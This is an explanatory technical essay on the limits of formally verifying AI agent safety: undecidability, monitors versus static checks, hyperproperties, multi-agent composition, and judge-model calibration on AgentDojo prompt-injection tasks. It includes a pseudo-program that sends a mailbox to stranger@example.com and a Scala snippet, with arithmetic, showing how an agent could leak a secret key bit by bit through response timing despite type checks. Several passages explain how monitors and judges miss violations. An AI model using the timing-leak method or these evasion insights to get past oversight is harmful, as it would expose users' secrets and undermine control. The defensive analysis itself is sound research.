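Two layers protect best when no single fault can defeat both. Containers and Bubblewrap both rely on the host's kernel, so a kernel flaw might let code escape from either. Moon and Varshney cite Copy Fail, a Linux kernel flaw that let a process gain extra privileges and went undiscovered for nearly a decade. A virtual machine is a more independent layer because it has its own kernel, but it still depends on the hardware and on the software that separates the machines.

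### Questions for a reviewer

Someone assessing a product that claims a guarantee for its agent could ask:

1. What exactly is the property, and which actions does it cover?
2. Can the agent cause an effect by any other route, such as a built-in tool, a plug-in or an external command?
3. What may each permitted command do once it starts, and can the agent edit any code that the command runs?
4. Which library code has a person marked as safe, and who reviews changes to it?
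5. Does the proof cover a small model of the language, the compiler or the code that actually runs?
6. Which versions did the developers check, and are those the versions in use?
7. Which remote services could change without notice, and does the guarantee depend on their behaviour?
8. If the checker crashes or runs out of time, does the action go ahead?
9. Has anyone used current frontier models to attack the system, and how quickly do fixes reach users?
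10. If the type checker failed completely, which files, accounts and networks could the agent still reach?

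## Which safety properties can these methods not express?

Even a flawless compiler, policy engine and operating system could not enforce every safety property, for four reasons. No algorithm can decide whether an arbitrary program will ever send a user's mailbox to a stranger. A monitor that observes only a single run cannot determine whether the user's private calendar influenced the behavior it observed. A proof that ignores time does not rule out an agent leaking a key through the timing of its actions. Finally, checking the form of an email cannot establish whether its contents are true.

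### Programs that no checker can settle

Rice's theorem, published by Henry Rice in 1953, concerns what programs do, as opposed to how their text looks. If some programs have a certain behaviour and others lack it, no algorithm can decide correctly for every program whether it has that behaviour. A checker can easily find out whether a program contains the word `send_email`. "Never sends the mailbox to a stranger" is a different matter. Take any program *Q* and build this one from it:

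```text
run Q, with no access to any tool
send the mailbox to stranger@example.com
```

Suppose a program runs another program, *Q*, and does something harmful only if *Q* stops. A perfect checker could then tell whether any *Q* stops, and Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no algorithm can do that for every *Q*. *No finite rulebook can certify every safe program* (Pérez-Acle, 2026) gives the example of a short program that searches the even numbers above 2 for one that is not the sum of two primes, and performs the forbidden action only if it finds one. The program is safe if and only if Goldbach's conjecture, an open problem in number theory, is true. Running it could expose a violation, but no number of steps without one would prove it safe.

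A restricted language avoids the problem. SPA's plans have six kinds of step, no functions, and loops only over the items of a collection, so nobody can write the search for a counterexample as a plan. But any work that needs general code has to happen in tools or the isolated model, where the plan checker does not analyze it.

A checker for a general language has to reject whatever it cannot prove safe. Pérez-Acle shows that every sound checker of this kind fails to approve infinitely many safe programs, including one about as long as the checker. That program searches for the checker's approval of its own code and performs the forbidden action if it finds that approval. Approval would make the program harmful, so a sound checker never approves it, and the program never performs the forbidden action.

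No user would need that program. In simulations on 2.2 million random programs, Pérez-Acle found that such obstacles come from adversarial programs and are not typical. Ordinary false rejections, such as when SPA blocks payment of a genuine invoice, do more harm to an agent's user.

If a program may run for only *T* steps, a checker can simulate all of them and give the right answer. But a checker that is always right must take roughly *T* steps on some programs. Otherwise, a program could run the checker on its own code within the limit and then do the opposite of what the checker predicts. A faster checker has to reject some harmless programs or leave them undecided.

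Policies can be undecidable too. *What Can Be Enforced?* (Ray, 2026) considers rules with counters that can go up and down and be tested for zero. Two such counters can encode any computation, so no tool can always tell whether a set of these rules would ever block anything. If counters can only go up, and rules can compare them only with fixed limits, the analysis always finishes. These restricted rules can still express a daily cap on transfers to each recipient and a ban on sending anything after the user revokes access. They cannot directly express a rolling 24-hour total, like the one in Dogwood's refund budget, because the total can fall.

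### Bad things and good things

A run is the sequence of events that a system produces. Properties of single runs come in two basic kinds:

- **Safety** means that something bad never happens. If a run breaks a safety property, some finite beginning of it is already beyond repair.
- **Liveness** means that something good eventually happens. However a run begins, it can still continue in a way that satisfies the property.

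In symbols, let *P* be the set of acceptable complete runs:

Let *P* be a set of runs. *P* is a safety property if every run outside *P* has a finite beginning with no continuation in *P*. It is a liveness property if every finite beginning has a continuation in *P*.

Every property of single runs is a combination of a safety property and a liveness property. Schneider (2000) proved in *Enforceable Security Policies* that a monitor which watches a program and stops it can enforce only safety properties. His example is a ban on sending messages after reading a file. The monitor needs two states, "no file read yet" and "file read", and stops the program if it tries to send a message in the "file read" state.

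Similar rules work for agents. *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (2025) proves that a history that obeys the rules still obeys them after any tool call its system allows. According to Ray, a gate like this, given reliable inputs, can enforce a policy without blocking any compliant run only if the policy is a safety property and the gate has enough memory to recognise the permitted histories.

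Such a gate cannot enforce the rule "every payment is eventually followed by a confirmation." It allows or blocks each payment before any confirmation, so it may allow a payment that the agent never confirms or block one that the agent would have confirmed. Scaffolding could enforce the rule by holding each payment until the agent has submitted the confirmation, but many confirmations make no sense before the payment has gone through.

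A deadline turns some liveness properties into safety properties. "Every customer eventually gets an answer" becomes "every customer gets an answer within an hour", which a run violates if an hour passes without an answer. A gate may still be unable to prevent the violation. *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited* (Basin, Jugé and colleagues) distinguishes the actions a mechanism can block from those it can only observe. A gate can block an email, but it can only observe time passing, and it cannot make the model write a reply.

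The scaffolding could send a standard reply itself after 55 minutes. A proof could then show, without assuming anything about the model, that every customer gets an answer if the mail service works, but it would not show that the answer is useful.

### Secrets and pairs of runs

Suppose Michelle's assistant reads her private calendar and then updates a public status page. Here are two programs it might run:

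| Program | Status if she has a medical appointment | Status if she has none |
|---|---|---|
| A | "Away" | "Away" |
| B | "Away" | "Here" |

Program A reads the calendar and posts "Away" every day, while program B reads it and posts "Away" only on days with an appointment. On a day with an appointment, a monitor observes the same events from both, but only B's post reveals the appointment to anyone who knows the code. A monitor that judges only the events must treat the programs alike, so it either blocks A, which is harmless, or permits B's leak.

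Noninterference requires that secret inputs never change public outputs, so it depends on what the program would have output if the secret inputs had been different. In *Hyperproperties*, Clarkson and Schneider (2009) gave such requirements their name. Let *T* be the set of all runs that a system can produce. An ordinary property is a set *P* of acceptable runs, and the system satisfies it if *T* ⊆ *P*. A hyperproperty is a set *H* of acceptable sets of runs, and the system satisfies it if *T* ∈ *H*.

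A monitor can instead enforce a stricter rule, such as a ban on posting anything after reading the calendar. Schneider notes that monitors claiming to prevent information flow do this. The stricter rule blocks A as well as B. A type system for information flow can do better because it analyzes the code for both days. It accepts A, whose post does not depend on the calendar, and rejects B. It is still an approximation, since it also rejects some harmless programs.

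Another method is to verify two copies of the program side by side. Both get the same public inputs but different calendars, and the verifier has to prove that their public outputs never differ. This is an ordinary safety property of the pair, so existing verifiers can handle it. Clarkson and Schneider generalise this to any hyperproperty whose violations always show up in at most *k* finite runs, using *k* copies. For an agent, the proof also has to assume that the model gives both copies the same replies whenever it has read the same text, because otherwise the outputs could differ by chance.

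Moon and Varshney assume the model could do anything, which can be misleading for hyperproperties. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that may output 0, 1 or a secret bit. Its possible outputs are 0 and 1 whatever the secret is, so the set of possible outputs reveals nothing about the secret. A system that always outputs the secret does only what the first system could have done, but it leaks the secret. A scaffold could likewise pass a check on its possible outputs with an arbitrary model and then leak with a particular one. Moon and Varshney's three rules for PocketFlow avoid this problem because each concerns single runs. The comparison of two copies also avoids it.

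Common languages for temporal rules cannot express such requirements. Clarkson, Finkbeiner and colleagues, in *Temporal Logics for Hyperproperties*, note that standard temporal logics refer to one run at a time, and propose logics that can refer to several. A Dogwood rule can refer to earlier events in a session, but it cannot compare that session with one that never took place. Finkbeiner (2025), in *Logics and Algorithms for Hyperproperties*, surveys methods for checking and monitoring such requirements. A monitor that stores many runs could catch program B if those runs included both kinds of day, but it could not establish that a program is free of leaks.

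### Checking, watching and rewriting

*Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms* (Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider, 2006) compares static checks and monitors with a third method, in which software rewrites the program before it runs. Here "yes" means the method can stop every violation without interfering with any compliant program.

| Policy | Static check | Monitor | Rewriting |
|---|---|---|---|
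| The program stops within 100 steps | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| The program never overwrites the disk's boot sector | No | Yes | Yes |
| The program behaves as if a secret file did not exist | No | No | Yes |

A static check cannot exactly enforce the rule against writing to the boot sector, because it would have to determine in advance whether an arbitrary program ever does so. A monitor can block the write when the program attempts it. A monitor can also run any static check when the program loads, so monitors are strictly more powerful than static checks if both have the same information.

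In practice, neither static checking nor runtime monitoring is always better. A monitor slows the program and may stop it halfway through a task. It also often has less information than a static check. A monitor inside the Java Virtual Machine, for example, has no access to Scala's capture sets. Hamlen and colleagues note that when a static check receives the source code and a monitor receives a version with some information erased, each may enforce policies the other cannot.

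For the secret file, the rewriter changes the folder-listing operation to omit the file. Programs that would have ignored the file behave as before, and those that would have reacted to it no longer can, so the rewriter never has to tell them apart. An agent's developer can do much the same with a listing tool that omits Michelle's private folder. When the task does not need the data, hiding it is therefore a better defence than trying to judge what the agent does with it.

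### One bit at a time

Odersky and colleagues exclude timing and termination from TACIT's guarantee. They mention that code working on classified data could leak one bit by taking more or less time depending on the content. A hostile agent can repeat this to leak more. Moon and Varshney's model of PocketFlow also omits timing.

Suppose a `Classified` container holds a 256-bit signing key, and the agent submits this snippet:

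```scala
key.map { k =>
  if bit(k, i) == 1 then countTo(veryLargeNumber) else 0L
}
```

`bit` and `countTo` only calculate, so the function is pure and the compiler accepts it. The agent sets `i` to 0 and times the reply, which is slow only if the bit is 1. After 256 calls the agent has the whole key, even though every call printed `Classified(****)`.

If an attacker can tell *m* different durations apart, each call carries up to log₂ *m* bits, so a key of *n* bits takes this many calls:

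> ⌈*n* / log₂ *m*⌉

With 16 distinguishable durations, the attacker needs only 64 calls. Noise makes the attack slower but does not prevent it. For example, the agent might go back to two durations, with each reading having an independent 10% chance of being wrong. If it takes the majority of nine readings for each bit, it has about an 80% chance of getting all 256 bits right. That requires 2,304 calls, or a little over six hours at ten seconds each, so an unattended agent could finish overnight.

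The agent may not even need a clock. If `countTo` never finished and the server reported a timeout, the error message would reveal the bit. Clarkson and Schneider point out that one well-known formal definition of secrecy permits such leaks.

The scaffolding can hold back every reply that involves classified data until, say, 30 seconds have passed, and return the same redacted text even if the snippet has not finished. This slows down quick tasks. The scaffolding can also limit the number of calls. If an agent learns 20 bits of a random 256-bit key, it still has 2²³⁶ possibilities to try, but a limit doesn't help when the secret is a single bit, such as whether Michelle is ill. TACIT's types could not confirm that either defence works, because they do not describe time.

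### What a message means

If the assistant writes to a supplier, "We paid your invoice yesterday," the tool call has the same types, labels and recipient whether or not the company paid. A checker that examines only the call therefore cannot determine whether the message is true.

Moon and Varshney put truthfulness, deception and manipulation outside their method because their policies can refer to an action and its effects, but not to what a message means. Deception is harder to define than falsehood, because a true statement can mislead. If the assistant overlooked a deadline that passed yesterday, it could truthfully write "nothing else in your inbox is due today". Whether a message manipulates someone also depends on the reader.

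The purpose of an action is often missing from the call as well. Ray demonstrated this with the final tool calls of 123 AgentDojo tasks. Each call came in two versions with the same action and instruction, but the instruction came from the user in one and from untrusted tool output in the other. A checker that sees only the action can't identify the unauthorised version better than chance. When Ray also showed judge models the source of the instruction, a model with 0.5 billion parameters still scored 50%, one with 3 billion scored 56.1%, and one with 7 billion scored 96.7%.

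Integrity labels record where data came from without needing a judge, so they can cover part of what people mean by purpose. But the model can still misunderstand an instruction that really came from Michelle and take an action she did not want. *Local Allow, Global Deny* (2026) treats purpose as a relation between different runs and concludes that guardrails that watch a single run cannot enforce it.

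### Harmless parts

As with the five refunds of $200, permitted actions can add up to a forbidden total. A rule that accounts for past actions can prevent this if every refund passes through one gate. Harm that builds up across several agents is harder to catch. For example, one agent may be able to read files but not use the network, while another can use the network but not read files. Neither can leak a document alone, but together they can if the first passes the text to the second.

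*Safety is Non-Compositional* (2026) proves that two agents can reach a forbidden capability together even if neither can reach one alone. *Runaway Reaction* (2026) shows a similar result for skills, the add-on packages that extend what an agent can do. Skills that are safe individually can be unsafe in combination, although every skill in a safe combination is itself safe.

*Pandora's Toolbox Or Why Agent Safety Cannot Be Verified* (2026) argues that an approved list of agents cannot capture which agents are safe together. Suppose a company wants a list such that two agents are safe together exactly when both are on it. Agents A1 and B1 each hold half of one password, and A2 and B2 each hold half of another. A1 and B2 are harmless together, so both belong on the list. So do A2 and B1, for the same reason. But then A1 and B1 are both on the list, and together they have a complete password.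 The company could leave some of the agents out, but that would ban harmless pairs.

*When Safe Skills Collide* (2026) looked for such combinations among 211,575 pairs of individually safe skills. A scanner flagged 47,075 pairs (22%) because together they had a risky combination of abilities, such as reading files and sending data out. Based on a human audit of 200 flagged cases, an estimated 18.2% of the flags were valid after weighting, which would be roughly 4% of all pairs. Even at that rate, an agent with 20 typical skills, which form 190 pairs, would have about eight risky pairs.

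Schneider found that several monitors on the same program enforce all their policies together. This does not hold when each agent has a separate monitor, because no monitor sees the whole exchange. *Pandora's Toolbox* notes that a monitor with access to every agent's context would reduce the problem to the single-agent case, but that agents may belong to different parties with their own safeguards.

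Harm can also be spread over time. Clarkson and Schneider consider a system that splits a secret into *k* shares and outputs one share per run. The violation is visible only to someone who compares *k* runs, and if the system may choose any *k*, no fixed number of copies of the system is enough for a proof. An agent could give away one share in each conversation, and stopping it would require a record that lasts across conversations. The survey *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (2026) describes a gap between the safety of single actions and the safety of whole tasks, which no current system closes reliably at scale.

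### Narrower tools and model judges

Developers can replace a property that software cannot check with a similar one that it can. For example, they could give the assistant a tool called `report_payment(invoice)` instead of letting it write freely to suppliers. The tool's code looks up the bank record and fills in a fixed sentence, so the message always matches the record, whatever the model does.

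This is probably the best option for routine messages. But it now guarantees only that a message agrees with a record, which may be wrong, and the agent can still mislead a supplier by reporting one invoice and leaving out another. The agent also can no longer explain why a payment is late.

The alternative is to keep free text and have another model judge it. A proof can establish that the agent sends no email without the judge's approval, but not that the judge is right. The guarantee no longer holds for every model and every input, and at best becomes a statistical one that the judge misses no more than a chosen share of violations on cases like those used for calibration.

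Ray calibrated 23 judges on 132 instructions from AgentDojo, of which 35 were malicious. When the target was to miss at most 5% of violations, every judge had to block everything. The small sample explains much of this. Each calibration used only half of the malicious instructions, which is fewer than the minimum of 19 examples that a 5% bound of this kind requires even for a perfect judge. With a 10% target, one of the better judges, Gemma-2-9B, missed 1% of the violations but blocked 78% of the harmless instructions.

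Ray also placed two small judges in front of a working agent for 949 attack trials each:

| Judge | Calls blocked | Successful attacks | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | None | 45 | 25.4% |
| 3 billion parameters | 78% | 4 | 18.0% |
| 7 billion parameters | 12% | 30 | 24.3% |

In paired reruns, a few attacks succeeded only when a judge was present, because blocking one call changes what the agent tries next.

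Stronger judges should make fewer mistakes, but their guarantee would have the same weakness, because an attacker does not draw cases at random from the calibration set. In another of Ray's tests, most judges missed more violations after small changes to the text they read, even though the action was unchanged. A judge is therefore useful for catching some harm that formal rules cannot describe, but it should not replace a rule that software can enforce exactly.

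### Properties and methods

In this table, "guaranteed" assumes the trusted base works and the rules are correct. Entries beginning with "if" include a further assumption, and "not expressible" means the method provides no way to state the property.

| Property | Schemas and capability types | Flow labels on a fixed plan | Policy engine or monitor | Proof about the scaffolding |
|---|---|---|---|---|
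| The agent calls only tools on a fixed list | Guaranteed | Guaranteed | Guaranteed | Guaranteed |
| No single refund exceeds $500 | If the refund library checks the amount | Not expressible | Guaranteed | Guaranteed |
| Refunds on one order never total more than $500 | If the refund library keeps the total | Not expressible | If its record covers every session | If its model covers every session |
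| The agent sends no email after reading a private file | Not expressible | Not expressible | Guaranteed | Guaranteed |
| Private data never changes public output, timing aside | If only pure code handles the data | If the run finishes normally | If a stricter rule is acceptable | If the proof compares two copies |
| Every customer eventually gets an answer | Not expressible | Not expressible | Not expressible | If the scaffolding sends a standard reply and the mail service works |
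| Response times reveal no secrets | Not expressible | Not expressible | If it delays every reply to a fixed time | If its model includes time |
| Two agents cannot leak a file together | If one compiler checks both agents' code | If both agents use the same labels | If it sees both agents' actions | If its model includes both agents |
| An email is true and does not mislead | Not expressible | Not expressible | Not expressible | Not expressible |
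| An action serves the user's purpose | Not expressible | Not expressible | Not expressible | Not expressible |
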